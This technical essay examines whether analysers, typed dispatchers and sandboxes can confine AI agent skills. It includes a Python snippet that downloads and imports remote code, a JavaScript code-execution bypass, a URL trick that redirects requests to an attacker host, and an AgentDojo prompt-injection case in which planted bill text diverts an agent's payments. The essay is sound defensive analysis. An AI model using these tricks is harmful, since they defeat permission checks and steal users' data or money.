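*Defensive Capability Analysis for JavaScript Libraries* (Xu and Møller, 2026) presents an analysis with this kind of guarantee for npm packages, the libraries that JavaScript programmers share. The analyser starts with a list of sensitive objects, such as the functions for reading files and for executing text as code. It also lists carrier objects, through which a program can reach the sensitive ones. It follows all these objects through assignments, property reads and calls to known built-in functions. If the program uses one at a place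 the analyser can identify, the analyser makes a direct report. If the program stores the object in a property or passes it to another function, the analyser stops following it and makes an indirect report, which lists every capability the object could provide.

### What the theorem assumes

**The analysis assumes that its table of library effects is complete.** Python can overwrite a file with `open`, `pathlib.Path.write_text`, `shutil.copy` and other functions. If the table lacks `shutil.copy` and the analyser treats unlisted functions as harmless, it reports ⊥ for a script that destroys a file. Treating every unlisted function as ⊤ avoids this but causes more false alarms. Xu and Møller compiled their table from earlier research and the official documentation of JavaScript and Node.js, the program that runs JavaScript outside a browser. They also had to inspect inherited methods, because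 an expression such as `eval.valueOf()` looks harmless but returns `eval` itself.

**The analyser also covers the libraries that the script uses.** On the script side, Metere's formal model contains only the skill's own programs. Xu and Møller show how an attacker can exploit such a limit. Their example package reads a "signature" from a data file and passes it to a popular library that rebuilds JavaScript objects from text. The signature makes the library build a function that deletes the computer's files. The package then passes this function to a second library, which calls it. Neither library is malicious, and the attacker's own code contains no suspicious call, so an analyser that ignores libraries reports nothing.

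Benign packages depend on libraries for their capabilities more than malicious ones do. Among the benign packages that use any capability, only 57% use one in their own code, compared with 99% of the malicious packages. The analysed version of a library also has to be the installed one. A skill's signature doesn't guarantee this, because it covers the skill's manifest and content but not a library that the user installs separately.

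**The analyser accounts for native code.** Many Python libraries contain compiled C code. If that code deletes a file, no delete call appears in the Python source. The rule for child processes does not cover this code, which runs inside the script's own process. The analyser has to treat such a library as ⊤, rely on a trusted table entry, or analyse the compiled code. Alpha-Omega, a Linux Foundation project, has a tool that finds the capabilities of Rust programs from LLVM bitcode, an intermediate form that many compilers produce. The project expects the static analysis to extend to other languages that use LLVM. The tool can also trace the system calls of any running program, but a trace covers only that run, so it cannot support the theorem.

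**The analyser has read all the code that will run.** A script that downloads text and passes it to `exec` goes to ⊤. These two lines achieve the same without `exec`:

```python
open("helper.py", "w").write(requests.get(url).text)
import helper
```

Python runs a module's code when a script imports it. `helper.py` does not exist during the analysis, so an analyser that skips missing modules reports only one network request and one file write, even though the downloaded code can do anything. To be sound, the analyser has to map an import to ⊤ unless it has read the exact file that Python will load.

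**Names in the source lead to the expected targets.** This premise fails in the hand analysis above because `requests.get` follows redirects by default, so the server at `api.example.com can` redirect the script to any other host. The session then contains a `net.egress` effect that *Ê*(*p*) does not cover, although every step of the analysis followed Metere's table. The table entry must cover every host unless the script turns redirects off or checks each new address. The same applies to summarise-fetched-html.

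The path `./.cache/../notes.txt` begins with the declared folder, `./.cache`, but leads out of it, so the analyser has to simplify paths before comparing them. Simplification is not enough if `.cache` is a symbolic link, a file-system entry that points to another folder. The analyser cannot detect such links from the source code, so the operator has to check for them on the machine or have the operating system confine the script to the declared folder.

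Metere's proof assumes that the analyser recognises every construct that can execute text as code. Xu and Møller found three JavaScript features that defeat their own analysis. One is that every function has a `constructor` property, which refers to an object that turns text into code. The expression `(function(){})[E]` returns this object whenever the variable `E` holds the string "constructor", even though nothing sensitive appears in the source.

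Covering these features in the analysis would have made it much less precise, so Xu and Møller block them while the program runs. Their guarantee holds only for programs that run under this protection. The protection interfered with the tests of 67 out of 3,682 projects, mostly because of testing and development tools. Two of the 1,311 malicious packages in their collection used the `constructor` route and escaped the static analysis, so the protection was necessary. A proof about a skill's scripts likewise has to specify the interpreter and settings they will run with.

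### The cost of sending every hard case to top

An analyser can satisfy nearly all these premises by returning ⊤ whenever it cannot determine an effect. This result is always sound, but no useful manifest can contain ⊤, so the script fails the check even if it is harmless.

Metere accepts this drawback, arguing that constructs such as `eval` are rare in well-curated skills and that the few skills that need them should not aim for a proof. As evidence, Metere cites the trials with destructive agents that underlie the "tested" level, but those trials did not examine how skill authors write scripts.

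The npm results suggest that such constructs are common in ordinary code. Xu and Møller analysed 5,685 popular packages together with their libraries and found possible code execution in 1,433 of them, or about a quarter. In 649 packages, the program executes fixed text, often to find out what environment it is running in. An analyser could analyse that text like any other code, but Metere's rule assigns ⊤ to the whole program. Skill scripts are probably shorter than npm packages and use fewer libraries, so the share among skills may be lower.

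Many of these reports are also false alarms. Xu and Møller checked 20 reports of each kind by hand to see whether the program used the capability. Direct reports were almost always right. Indirect reports were right 90% of the time for files and for starting processes, but only 20% of the time for the network, 10% for code execution and never for loading modules under names chosen at run time. The rates differ because of how JavaScript provides these capabilities. A program that loads the file-system module usually uses files. But code execution is also available through the global object, which programs pass around for many harmless reasons, and each time the analyser has to assume that the program might execute code.

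Even so, about 70% of all reports were correct, partly because the analysis has narrower fallbacks than Metere's. When it can no longer track the file-system module, it reports only file operations. 59% of the packages used no capabilities, even counting their libraries, so a sound analyser can clear much ordinary code without false alarms.

Metere would reserve the effort of proof for a few skills, including those that use `spawn.proc`. But the rule for child processes assigns ⊤ to a script that starts `git` or a video converter, because those programs are not part of the skill. The method can therefore prove containment for a skill that starts processes only if the skill ships the source of every program it starts, or if someone writes a trusted summary of each external program.

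Skill authors can avoid some of these failures by writing scripts that are easier to analyse. A script can read data with a JSON parser instead of `eval`, choose functions from a fixed list instead of looking them up by name, and check any host it receives against a short list of permitted ones. Under Metere's scheme, authors have little reason to do this, because a skill that fails the analysis can still run at the "tested" level with the same automatic approvals, and the scripts the analysis could not resolve run with the user's full access.

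## How closely existing skill analysers meet the theory

The soundness theorem for static analysis applies only to an analyser whose transfer functions cover every effect a script can have. The developers of two open-source programs claim to have built such an analyser for agent skills. One program ships with enclawed, and the other is SkillFortify, a Python tool that scans skills before installation. Both search files for known text patterns, which is fast but doesn't provide the coverage the theorem requires.

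### The scanner in enclawed

Metere suggests building the analyser on an existing engine such as Semgrep or CodeQL, and the results for summarise-fetched-html come from Semgrep. The analyser that ships with enclawed instead searches every Python, shell, JavaScript and TypeScript file stored with SKILL.md using regular expressions for that language, which match patterns of characters such as `open` followed by a bracket. Each match adds a capability to the result. A match for a construct that runs text as code, such as `eval`, `exec` or a dynamic import, sets the result to ⊤.

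In the paper on enclawed, Metere calls this result a "sound over-approximation". Let *R* be the set of patterns and eff(*r*) the effect attached to pattern *r*. The scanner computes

*Ê*(*p*) = ⋃ { eff(*r*) : *r* ∈ *R* and *r* matches the text of *p* }.

If no pattern matches, the result is ⊥, meaning that the script has no effects. A sound analyser instead returns ⊤ for anything it does not recognise. Adding patterns reduces missed effects, but soundness requires a matching pattern for every effect in *E*(*p*), and a text search cannot establish that.

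A scanner that searches for text patterns can miss some of a script's effects or report effects it doesn't have. Suppose a skill gets exchange rates by calling `client.latest_rates()` from a bank's own Python library. The call contacts the network, but the scanner is likely to miss it because a general set of patterns is unlikely to include its name. Another script may mention `requests.get(` in a comment but never use the network, and the scanner can still report network access.

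The rule that maps reflective constructs to ⊤ has the same weakness, because it applies only when a pattern matches one. It can also reject harmless code. Scripts that use the machine-learning library PyTorch often call `model.eval()` to switch a neural network from training to evaluation mode, and a loosely written pattern would treat this call as code execution.

Scanners also have difficulty determining the targets of effects. In the exchange-rate script analysed by hand in the previous section, the address passed to `requests.get` contains the variable `host`, which may hold either of two names. A scanner that looks only at the call cannot determine which. It can report that the script may contact any host, but then the script fails against any manifest that names particular hosts. Or it can guess the host from names elsewhere in the file, which is unsound.

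enclawed has 53 tests for its three methods and the evidence bundle. Some of them check that the patterns match the text they should match. Metere lists no test that runs a script, records its effects and compares them with the scanner's result. Such a test could not prove soundness, but a single missed effect would disprove it.

Metere also claims that the static method eliminates attacks in which a script exceeds its manifest, provided the analyser is sound for the script's language. enclawed's scanner does not meet this condition, so the claim does not extend to the skills it passes. It can still catch an honest author's forgotten declaration, and the design lets an operator replace the scanner with a stronger engine.

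### Where effects escape a text search

The gaps come from ordinary language features that also appear in benign code. For example, the common Python line `import numpy as np` gives a library a new name.

| Feature | Why a text search may miss the effect | What a sound analyser has to do |
|---|---|---|
| Renaming, and functions stored in variables | The call need not contain the function's usual name | Track which functions each variable may hold |
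| Libraries | The effect occurs in a file outside the skill | Analyse the installed version or use a trusted summary |
| Names computed from data | The name exists only while the script runs | Report the effects of every function the name could refer to |
| Implicit calls | Reading a property or using an operator can run a function | Include the functions that the language calls by itself |
| Compiled code | No source text is available | Report ⊤ or use a trusted summary |
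| Code in unusual files | The scanner chooses files by their type | Cover every file that an interpreter may load |

### SkillFortify's lattice and its three phases

SkillFortify has a more detailed theory than enclawed's scanner. It accepts Claude Code skills, OpenClaw skills and configuration files for servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting language models to tools.

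Its lattice has four levels of access:

NONE ⊑ READ ⊑ WRITE ⊑ ADMIN.

SkillFortify defines a capability set by assigning one access level to each of eight resources: the file system, the network, environment variables, the shell, other skills, the clipboard, the browser and databases. READ permits observation, WRITE also permits changes, and ADMIN adds the right to grant or revoke other parties' access. One capability set is below another if it has no higher level for any resource. The join of two sets takes the higher level for each resource.

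These sets are coarser than Metere's because they contain no hosts or file paths, so a skill with READ access to the network may read from any host. But SkillFortify has an entry for environment variables, which Metere's vocabulary lacks. The lattice is also small enough to need no widening. Each of the eight resources can go up only three levels, so a capability set can grow at most 24 times. The soundness proof gives the lattice's height as 4⁸ = 65,536, but that is the number of possible capability sets.

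The analysis has three phases:

1. The analyser infers a capability set, written *Cap*_I(*s*) for a skill *s*. A web address in the text sets the network level to at least READ, and the name of an HTTP method that changes data raises it to WRITE. A shell command sets the shell level to WRITE. Other rules cover environment variables, file operations and the remaining resources.
2. The analyser searches for dangerous patterns, such as a downloaded file passed straight to a shell. Each pattern has a severity and a type of attack. A separate rule, which the developer calls information-flow analysis, looks for text encoding combined with access to an outside network.
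3. If the skill declares a capability set, *Cap*_D(*s*), the analyser compares the two sets. A resource is a violation if its inferred level exceeds its declared level.

Suppose a skill's text contains a web address and a command that writes a file. The analyser infers READ for the network and WRITE for the file system. If the manifest declares WRITE for the network but only READ for the file system, the write access to the file system is a violation.

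### What the soundness theorem covers

SkillFortify's main theorem concerns a skill without violations. It states that whenever such a skill accesses a resource *r* at level ℓ, in any execution, ℓ ⊑ *Cap*_D(*s*)(*r*). The proof joins two inequalities:

ℓ ⊑ *Cap*_I(*s*)(*r*) ⊑ *Cap*_D(*s*)(*r*).

The second follows from the comparison in phase 3. The first depends on a lemma that the level assigned by a phase 1 rule covers the program states matching the detected pattern. The lemma does not apply to code that no pattern matches, and the analyser leaves the level of such code at NONE.

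A skill can declare NONE for every resource but send data through a library that the rules do not recognise. The analyser then infers NONE for every resource and finds no violation. Read literally, the theorem implies that the skill never accesses the network, which is false.

The rules can also be wrong about code they match. Each rule sets a minimum level, but an over-approximation needs a maximum. When the analyser finds a web address, the proof assumes that the skill only reads from it. If the skill instead sends data through a library function whose name contains none of the listed methods, the analyser infers READ for an operation that needs WRITE.

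Let *X*(*s*) be the operations that the analyser extracts from the skill and *P*(*s*) the operations that the skill can perform. If each rule assigns a high enough level to the operations it matches, the argument proves the narrower result that every operation in *X*(*s*) stays within the declared set. Containment also requires *P*(*s*) ⊆ *X*(*s*), which SkillFortify cannot establish.

SkillFortify's developer accepts a limit of this kind, describing the program as sound with respect to the operations it extracts. The theorem does not cover commands assembled at run time or addresses read from a file. This excludes a good deal of ordinary code, since many programs read addresses from a settings file.

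The program also makes no repeated passes over loops, although the theory defines them. The developer's justification is correct here, because the rules only record that a feature is present and never lower a level, so a second pass would add nothing. The hand analysis of the exchange-rate script needed further passes because it tracked the value of `page`, whereas SkillFortify tracks no values.

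The theory includes an attacker model adapted from Dolev and Yao's work on network protocols. The attacker can intercept, replace and suppress skill packages, write new ones and alter registries, but cannot forge signatures. A separate theorem shows that no attacker within the model is stronger than this one. The theorem does not help the static analysis, because even a weak attacker who can write a skill can use code that the rules don't recognise.

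### The 540-skill benchmark

The developer tested SkillFortify on 540 generated skills, half malicious and half benign, divided equally among the three formats. A skill counted as flagged if the analyser reported at least one finding of medium or higher severity. SkillFortify flagged 250 of the 270 malicious skills (92.6%) and none of the benign ones.

| Type of attack | Found |
|---|---|
| Code execution, file tampering, privilege escalation, hidden data in other content, reverse shells and cryptocurrency mining | 126 of 126 |
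| Sending data out over HTTP or DNS | 45 of 48 |
| Theft of credentials | 29 of 30 |
| Encoded or obfuscated programs | 25 of 26 |
| Prompt injection | 21 of 24 |
| Typosquatting | 4 of 8 |
| Dependency confusion | 0 of 8 |

Dependency confusion and typosquatting account for 12 of the 20 misses. In dependency confusion, an attacker publishes a skill under the same name as a company's private skill, so that the installer fetches the wrong one. In typosquatting, the name is a slight misspelling of a popular skill's name. To detect either attack, an analyser needs a list of legitimate names, which the contents of one skill do not provide. Of the 20 misses, 14 were MCP configurations, which often contain little more than one command and its arguments.

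The information-flow rule fired 44 times but added no detections, because other patterns had already flagged the same skills. The developer had expected it to catch attacks too spread out for a single pattern to match, and an earlier version of the evaluation had reported a benefit. The benchmark contains no attack of that kind, so the result doesn't show whether the technique would work on one.

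The benchmark probably overstates how well the patterns detect attacks, because the developer drew both the patterns and the attack types largely from the same two collections, the ClawHavoc reports and a set of synthetic malicious tools called MalTool. Each malicious skill also contains only one type of attack. The developer treats 92.6% as a lower bound for attacks visible in a skill's contents, but acknowledges that real skills may combine attacks or use obfuscation missing from the benchmark. Either could lower the detection rate in practice.

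### Why zero false alarms is no evidence of soundness

Soundness limits what an analyser may miss but does not limit its false alarms. Sound analysers therefore tend to raise too many, and in the extreme case a program that rejects every skill misses no attacks but flags every benign skill. The opposite extreme is a program that approves every skill, which raises no false alarms but misses every attack.

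One passage in the latest version of the evaluation wrongly states that soundness guarantees that every reported finding is a genuine violation. The next part corrects this and attributes the lack of false alarms to the reporting threshold and to benign examples generated without malicious behaviour. The 95% confidence interval for the false-alarm rate extends to 1.4%, but it applies only to skills generated in the same way. Real skills are harder to clear as safe because many harmless ones use a shell.

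The benchmark also does not test containment, the property the theorem concerns. It labels skills as malicious or benign, but either kind can stay within its permissions or exceed them. To test containment, the developer would have had to record what each skill did and compare that with its inferred capability set. Pattern matching alone produced all 250 detections, so the capability check accounted for none of them.

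SkillFortify's developer is more cautious than the theorem and limits the guarantee to the behaviours that the analyser models. The developer calls the catalogue of those behaviours "necessarily partial" and says that SkillFortify is not sound as a malware detector. Cisco gives a similar warning about its own skill scanner: "no findings does not mean no risk".

SkillFortify's trust labels are less rigorous. The program combines four scores between 0 and 1, weighting the author's identity and the static analysis at 0.3 each, and community use and past vulnerabilities at 0.2 each. A skill with a total of at least 0.75 receives the label "formally verified". Only a skill without findings scores 1 on static analysis, but a score of 0.17 is enough for the label if the other three scores are perfect and the skill has no dependencies. The total also decays over time, so a skill that starts at 0.85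 loses the label after 13 days without an update.

### General-purpose analysers

Metere regards Semgrep, CodeQL and Pyright as mature engines that need only a table linking library calls to capabilities. They would be a large improvement on regular expressions. Semgrep and CodeQL parse the program and can track values through it, so they can handle renamed functions and many variables. Pyright, a Python type checker, would contribute less because Python's types do not record effects.

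To make one of these engines sound, an operator would have to supply the table and also change how the engine handles calls it can't resolve. Developers use Semgrep and CodeQL to find vulnerabilities in large projects, where thousands of false alarms would make the results useless. When the engine can't tell which function a call reaches, it usually ignores the possible targets. An analyser has to report them to prove containment, so the operator can expect many more false alarms after the change.

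Livshits and colleagues coined "soundy" for analyses that handle most of a language soundly but deliberately leave out a few difficult features, such as reflection and native code. They argued that nearly all practical whole-program analyses are soundy, and that their developers should say which features they leave out. For an agent skill, the evidence could include the claim that the scripts stay within *D* unless they use a listed feature. A second check could then reject scripts containing those features or block them at run time, as Xu and Møller do for JavaScript.

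Google's Capslock analyses the capabilities of ordinary Go packages. It follows calls from a package, through its dependencies, to standard library functions that use the network, files or other protected resources. This is easier in Go than in Python because values have static types and the source of most dependencies is available. Capslock also reports features that limit the analysis, including reflection, unsafe memory access and calls to C code, in separate categories, so an operator can refuse a package that uses them.

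### A language the analyser can cover

An analyser for skills could reach the theorem's standard by accepting only a small language. Astrée, which uses abstract interpretation, proved that flight software for the Airbus A380 has no run-time errors. The absence of such errors is undecidable for programs in general, although SkillFortify's developer explains Astrée's stronger guarantee by saying that it is decidable from the program text. Astrée's original version could give a sound answer because it covered a restricted form of C, without recursion or dynamic memory allocation, and over-approximated what it could not compute exactly.

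Starlark, a Python-like language that the Bazel build tool uses, has no built-in functions for opening files or network connections. A Starlark program can open them only through functions that the application running it supplies. A skill runtime could likewise supply one function for each capability, so its table of effects would be complete by design.

Even a simple search for names could then be sound, provided a script could not obtain an effectful function without naming it. The analyser would parse the script, collect the names of any supplied functions that appear in it and report their capabilities. If there were none, the script would have no outside effects. The analyser would still have to track hosts and paths, or report every possible target.

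However, skill authors would have to rewrite their scripts. A skill that fills in PDF forms may depend on a large Python library, which the runtime would have to supply as a function with its own trusted summary. For existing skills, it is often more practical to leave the script as it is and restrict the process that runs it.

### A sandbox that enforces the inferred set

A sandbox limits what a program can do while it runs. Metere discusses gVisor, which intercepts a program's calls to the operating system, and WASI, an interface that gives WebAssembly programs access only to the resources they are given. Metere objects that a sandbox cannot check whether a call matches the manifest the operator approved. The runtime can remove this objection for files and network connections by generating the sandbox's rules from the manifest.

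Let *A* be the set of effects that the sandbox allows. If the sandbox works correctly, every effect of the script lies in *A*. The runtime can set *A* = *Ê*(*p*) after checking that *Ê*(*p*) ⊆ *D*. The script then stays within its permissions even if *Ê*(*p*) is incomplete, because the sandbox blocks any effect that the analyser missed. The operator relies on the sandbox for safety and on the analyser only for an accurate list of what the script needs.

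This arrangement also makes child processes easier to analyse. If a program such as `git`, to which Metere's static rule would assign ⊤, runs under the same restrictions as the script, the operator does not need its source code to know that it cannot go beyond *A* either. The runtime could also give the script a temporary copy of a folder and discard the changes if the task fails, which would make many direct file writes reversible.

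enclawed already does something similar for extensions, which are add-on modules other than skills. An extension that uses the network has to list its permitted hosts in a signed manifest. In enclawed's strict mode, it must also have reached at least the "tested" level. While the extension runs, a guard narrows the general list of allowed hosts to those in the manifest and records attempts to reach any other. Like enclawed's general network guard, this one does not cover a skill's Python script, for which Metere recommends packet filters and isolated network environments. SkillFortify's theory includes a sandbox that checks every action against the declared set, but the developer has not built it.

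An operating-system sandbox cannot enforce every capability in Metere's vocabulary. A payment and a request for exchange rates may both use encrypted connections to the same bank. The sandbox can allow or block the connection, but it cannot distinguish `pay` from `net.egress`. To control payments, the runtime has to withhold the bank credentials from the script and offer a separate payment function, which checks the recipient and the amount before it contacts the bank.

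## Refinement types at the point where tool calls are dispatched

Metere's second method controls the tool calls that the model requests, by giving the runtime's dispatch function a refinement type.

### What a refinement type adds

An ordinary type such as `Int` limits a value to the set of whole numbers. A refinement type adds a condition that narrows that set, as Jhala and Vazou explain in *Refinement Types* (2020).

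*Standard Refinement Types*, a set of teaching slides for the verifier Liquid Haskell, uses division as an example. The function `divx` divides 42 by its argument, so it fails if the argument is 0. Its refined type is

{ *x* : Int | *x* ≠ 0 } → Int.

The verifier now rejects a call to `divx` unless it can prove the argument is not 0. It accepts *y*·*y* + 1, which is never 0. To decide such cases, it passes a formula to an SMT solver, which looks for a value that fits everything known about the argument but breaks the condition. If the solver proves that no such value exists, the call is safe.

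The example program in the slides then reads a number from the keyboard. The user could type 0, so the verifier rejects a direct call to `divx` with that number. The programmer has to add a test, `if i /= 0`, and call `divx` only in the branch where the test succeeds. In that branch, the verifier adds *i* ≠ 0 to the facts it gives the solver and accepts the call. Jhala and Vazou call this path-sensitive reasoning.

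### From a JSON message to a typed envelope

Metere gives dispatch the type

dispatch_M : { *e* : Envelope | cap(*e*) ∈ *D* } → Result,

where *M* is the manifest and cap(*e*) is the capability that the envelope *e* requires. The model's envelope reaches the runtime as JSON, a text format for structured data. Like the number from the keyboard, it could contain anything. In pseudocode, the runtime handles it like this:

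```
receive(text):
    e = parse(text)           // stops if the text is not a valid envelope
    if cap(e) in D:
        return dispatch(e)    // type-checks, because the test succeeded
    else:
        return deny(e)        // dispatch(e) would be a type error here
```

The parser checks only that the message has the right shape. Common tool-calling interfaces check about this much, using a JSON Schema, which lists the permitted fields and values. The next line tests whether cap(*e*) ∈ *D*, and the type checker treats this condition as true in the first branch.

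If a programmer deletes the test, the call to dispatch no longer type-checks and the build fails. The build also fails if someone adds a retry routine that dispatches a queued envelope without testing it. The types therefore prove that no path through the checked code dispatches an envelope without testing it.

The runtime must determine cap(*e*) from the requested operation and its arguments. If it read the capability from a field that the model fills in, a manipulated model could label a payment `fs.read`. The operator therefore also has to trust the table that maps operations to capabilities. Shell commands are the hardest case because such a table would require `spawn.proc` for running `rm budget.csv`, even though the command deletes a file.

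Poll (2024), in *Secure Input Handling*, attributes most security vulnerabilities to insecure input handling and warns against confusing validation with sanitisation. Validation rejects a bad input, while sanitisation changes it to make it safe. A dispatcher should normally validate, because changing an envelope after a human has approved it would make the runtime carry out a request that nobody approved.

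### What the compiler can reject

Metere claims that the method makes dispatching an envelope outside *D* a compile-time error, and that such calls are "typed-out before the gate is even consulted". This is true of the runtime's source code but not of the model's output, because the developers compile the runtime before the session starts, when the envelope does not yet exist. The compiler can reject code that would dispatch an envelope without testing it, but an envelope outside *D* can only be rejected by the test during the session.

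*Concordat* (2026), which adapts typed protocols to agents, identifies the same obstacle. Such protocols assume that a type checker can examine every party, but it cannot examine a language model. If a planted instruction leads the model to request a payment, the run-time test stops the payment, as an ordinary gate would.

Metere criticises policy engines such as Cedar, which decide whether a given user may perform a given action, because they check each request only when it arrives. These engines do not prove that the agent cannot issue a forbidden request, and neither does refinement-typed dispatch. Its advantage over an ordinary gate is the assurance that the runtime's programmers have left no way to dispatch a tool call without checking it.

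Metere also argues that developers should not keep both a type-level guarantee and a run-time check of the same condition, because a maintainer might delete the check in the belief that the types make it unnecessary. But the pseudocode needs both, because the check establishes the fact that the type requires, and the type forces every caller to obtain that fact. Compilers usually erase refinements, so a runtime that kept the type but dropped the check would have nothing to stop a forbidden envelope.

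The advice makes more sense for a second test of the same condition after the first has succeeded. Even then, the second test takes very little time and offers some protection if a programmer has overridden the type checker.

### Four ways to build the dispatcher

| Option | What a tool checks before the session | How a forbidden envelope could still get through |
|---|---|---|
| TypeScript branded type | callers pass only values that carry the brand | a wrong test, or code that forges the brand |
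| Liquid Haskell | the test implies the condition on every path to dispatch | callers in unchecked code, or a build that skips the verifier |
| F* | the same, as part of the language | callers in unchecked code |
| enclawed's frozen dispatcher | the dispatcher's answer for each capability name | any code that calls the host directly |

All four test each envelope at run time. They differ in how much they establish about the surrounding code.

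A branded type in TypeScript is an ordinary type with a marker that exists only for the compiler. A test function grants the brand, and dispatch accepts only branded envelopes. The compiler does not check that the test is correct, so a function that always returns true grants the same brand. A programmer can also forge the brand with a type cast, or turn off checking with the type `any`. Metere suggests generating a type for each skill that lists the capabilities in its manifest. The runtime would have to compile this type when it loads the skill, and would still need a test for the incoming JSON.

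Liquid Haskell uses a solver to confirm that the test implies the condition. Its types can also refer to earlier arguments of the same function:

dispatch : (*d* : Set Capability) → { *e* : Envelope | cap(*e*) ∈ *d* } → Result.

Here *d* is an ordinary value that the runtime reads from the manifest, so one successful check covers every skill. The programmer writes the refinements in special comments, which the standard Haskell compiler ignores. F*, a language designed for verification, has refinements built in and lets programmers supply proofs where the solver needs help.

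Metere expects that moving to either language would require only a one-time port of dispatch, with the rest of the runtime unchanged. But the callers would still be in JavaScript, where neither verifier can check them, so the ported module would have to accept raw JSON and perform the test itself.

enclawed uses no refinement-type checker. Its function `buildRefinedDispatch` takes a manifest and returns a dispatcher that throws a `RefinementError` when an envelope's capability is outside *D*. The dispatcher is frozen, which means that later code cannot alter its properties. To produce evidence for a skill, enclawed tries the dispatcher on every capability name in the vocabulary. As long as the decision depends only on the name, this covers every case in the vocabulary and is good evidence that the dispatcher works. It provides no evidence about the rest of the runtime, which is where the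 type would have helped.

### The theorem and its structural premise

Metere's theorem states that if dispatch_M type-checks with the refined input, no envelope whose capability is outside *D* can reach a host function through the runtime, whatever the model does.

The theorem's condition is too weak as stated. When a type checker checks a function with a refined input, it assumes that the input satisfies the refinement, and each caller has to prove it. For example, `divx` type-checks because the checker assumes that *x* is not 0. Likewise, dispatch can type-check even if a caller passes it an untested envelope. The theorem needs every caller to type-check, in a language whose type system is sound. The proof cites sound refinement systems such as those of Liquid Haskell and F*, but Metere recommends TypeScript as the simplest option, and TypeScript allows unsound code by design.

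The theorem also assumes that no call to the host bypasses dispatch. Metere calls this a structural invariant that someone can check once, by inspection or with a separate analyser. In practice, someone has to repeat the check whenever the runtime changes.

Extensions to enclawed can bypass its dispatcher, which Metere describes as the runtime's only route to the host's functions. They run in the same JavaScript process, so an extension that imports the standard file library can delete a file without creating an envelope. The open version of enclawed loads unsigned extensions with a warning and the strict version refuses them, but a signed extension can still make direct calls. Metere's tests confirm that the dispatcher throws an error when it should, but none of those listed checks for calls that bypass it.

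Developers can enforce part of this premise with types. If the function that deletes files requires a tested envelope, and no other module may import the original library function, a call that skips the test fails to compile. Running extensions in a separate process is safer. The operating system can deny that process access to files and the network, so it must send its requests to dispatch.

Another difficulty arises when several skills are active, because each dispatcher enforces one manifest but an envelope does not identify its skill. Metere claims that permissions cannot pass between skills because each skill has its own dispatcher. But if the model can choose the dispatcher, a manipulated model can choose the one that permits the payment. The theorem then limits the session only to the union of all the declared sets.

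### Harmful arguments to permitted tools

A check on the capability name does not examine how the model uses a permitted tool. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) gives two examples from the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants malicious instructions in the data an agent reads. In one, the user asks the agent to pay a bill that contains an instruction to send money to an attacker's account. The agent calls `send_money`, the tool it needs for the user's task, with the attacker's account as the recipient. In the other, it sends the attacker $0 with the user's scheduled payments in the subject line. Both calls pass a check that only tests whether *D* contains `pay`.

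The refinement can also cover the targets. Let *D* contain pairs (*c*, *t*) of a capability and a permitted target pattern. The accepted envelopes are then

{ *e* : Envelope | there is a (*c*, *t*) in *D* with cap(*e*) = *c* and target(*e*) matching *t* }.

For the exchange-rate skill from the first section, the condition on *e* could be:

```
   (cap(e) = tool.invoke and tool(e) = "fetch_rates")
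or (cap(e) = net.egress  and host(e) = "api.example.com")
or (cap(e) = fs.read     and resolve(path(e)) is inside "/home/ana/budget/")
```

This rejects both requests to `attacker.example` and attempts to read the user's private keys. The static analysis still has to check what `fetch_rates` does once it is running.

The result depends on how the runtime computes `host` and `resolve`. In `https://api.example.com@attacker.example/`, the permitted name comes before the @, so it is treated as a user name and the request goes to `attacker.example`. enclawed's network guard prevents this by using the standard web address parser and rejecting addresses that contain login details. Dispatch should do the same and pass the parsed address to the network function, so that dispatch and the network function cannot parse the text differently.

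For files, `resolve` has to follow symbolic links and remove steps such as `..`. Another program could still replace a link between the test and the read. To prevent this, the runtime can open the file first, check which file it opened, and read from that open file.

Some conditions depend on earlier events as well as on the envelope. For example, an airline may allow a refund only after the customer has confirmed it, so the refinement needs the session's history as a second argument. *Concordat* presents a related approach in which each tool is available only in certain states of the conversation, and only a person can take the confirmation step. In airline tasks that put pressure on the agent, a standard agent broke the confirmation rule with two different models, while the Concordat agent never broke it and completed about as many tasks.

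### How much one permitted call can leak

Metere also claims a numerical limit on what a manipulated model can leak through dispatch. The argument treats dispatch as a function π that maps each envelope to its capability if that is in *D*, and to "deny" otherwise. This function has at most |*D*| + 1 possible outputs, so each output carries at most

log₂(|*D*| + 1) bits.

Three declared capabilities give four outputs, so the limit is 2 bits per envelope. Metere supports the argument with the data-processing inequality, the information theory theorem that processing a message cannot increase the information it carries about its source.

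The inequality is correct, but π does not describe dispatch, because it outputs only the name of the capability, while dispatch also passes the arguments to the host. Suppose the exchange-rate skill is allowed to contact `api.example.com`, and the model can add a 100-character query to the address. If each character is one of 64 symbols, it carries log₂ 64 = 6 bits, so the query carries 600 bits. This is 300 times the claimed limit and enough for two 256-bit encryption keys.

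A correct limit has to count the permitted arguments. If *N*_c is the number of different arguments that dispatch accepts for capability *c*, the limit is

log₂(1 + Σ *N*_c) bits, summed over all *c* in *D*.

This equals Metere's formula only if each capability allows exactly one argument. Suppose the skill may call one tool, read one file and request rates for 29 currencies from one fixed address. There are then 1 + 1 + 1 + 29 = 32 outcomes, so the limit is 5 bits. If the skill may instead send any query to one fixed host, the limit is hundreds of bits or more.

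Restricting arguments is necessary even to get near log₂(|*D*| + 1), whereas Metere suggests summarising them or removing sensitive content at dispatch as ways to get below it. The corrected formula also covers only the content of a single envelope, not the timing of calls, the model's messages to the user or leaks across several permitted calls.

### A gate with a proved decision procedure

Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LEANGUARD*, present a gate whose rules can refer to a call's arguments, the state of a database and earlier events. They wrote it in Lean 4, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. LeanGuard admits a call only if all of the following hold:

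- at least one rule permits it;
- it meets every applicable requirement;
- no prohibition applies;
- no error occurs while the gate evaluates the relevant rules.

The gate therefore refuses a call when data is missing. When the developers build a policy, Lean checks a proof that the gate's decision matches the policy's logical definition for every possible history. During a session, the gate treats each call as untrusted data and evaluates the rules on it, with no further proof. The pseudocode above separates proof from run-time testing in the same way.

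Like Metere's theorem, the guarantee depends on every consequential call passing through the gate. It also depends on the accuracy of the component that reports the database's state. People have to ensure that the rules express the written policy. Sankar and colleagues had a language model draft the rules, then corrected the drafts by hand.

The evaluation used five Qwen models on τ²-bench, in which an agent serves simulated customers under a company's written policy. Without the gate, the agents executed at least 33 calls that the formal policy forbids; with it, they executed none. They completed 72.7% of tasks without the gate, 70.9% when the gate's refusals included an explanation, and 68.9% when they did not. The drop from 72.7% was statistically significant only when the refusals had no explanation.

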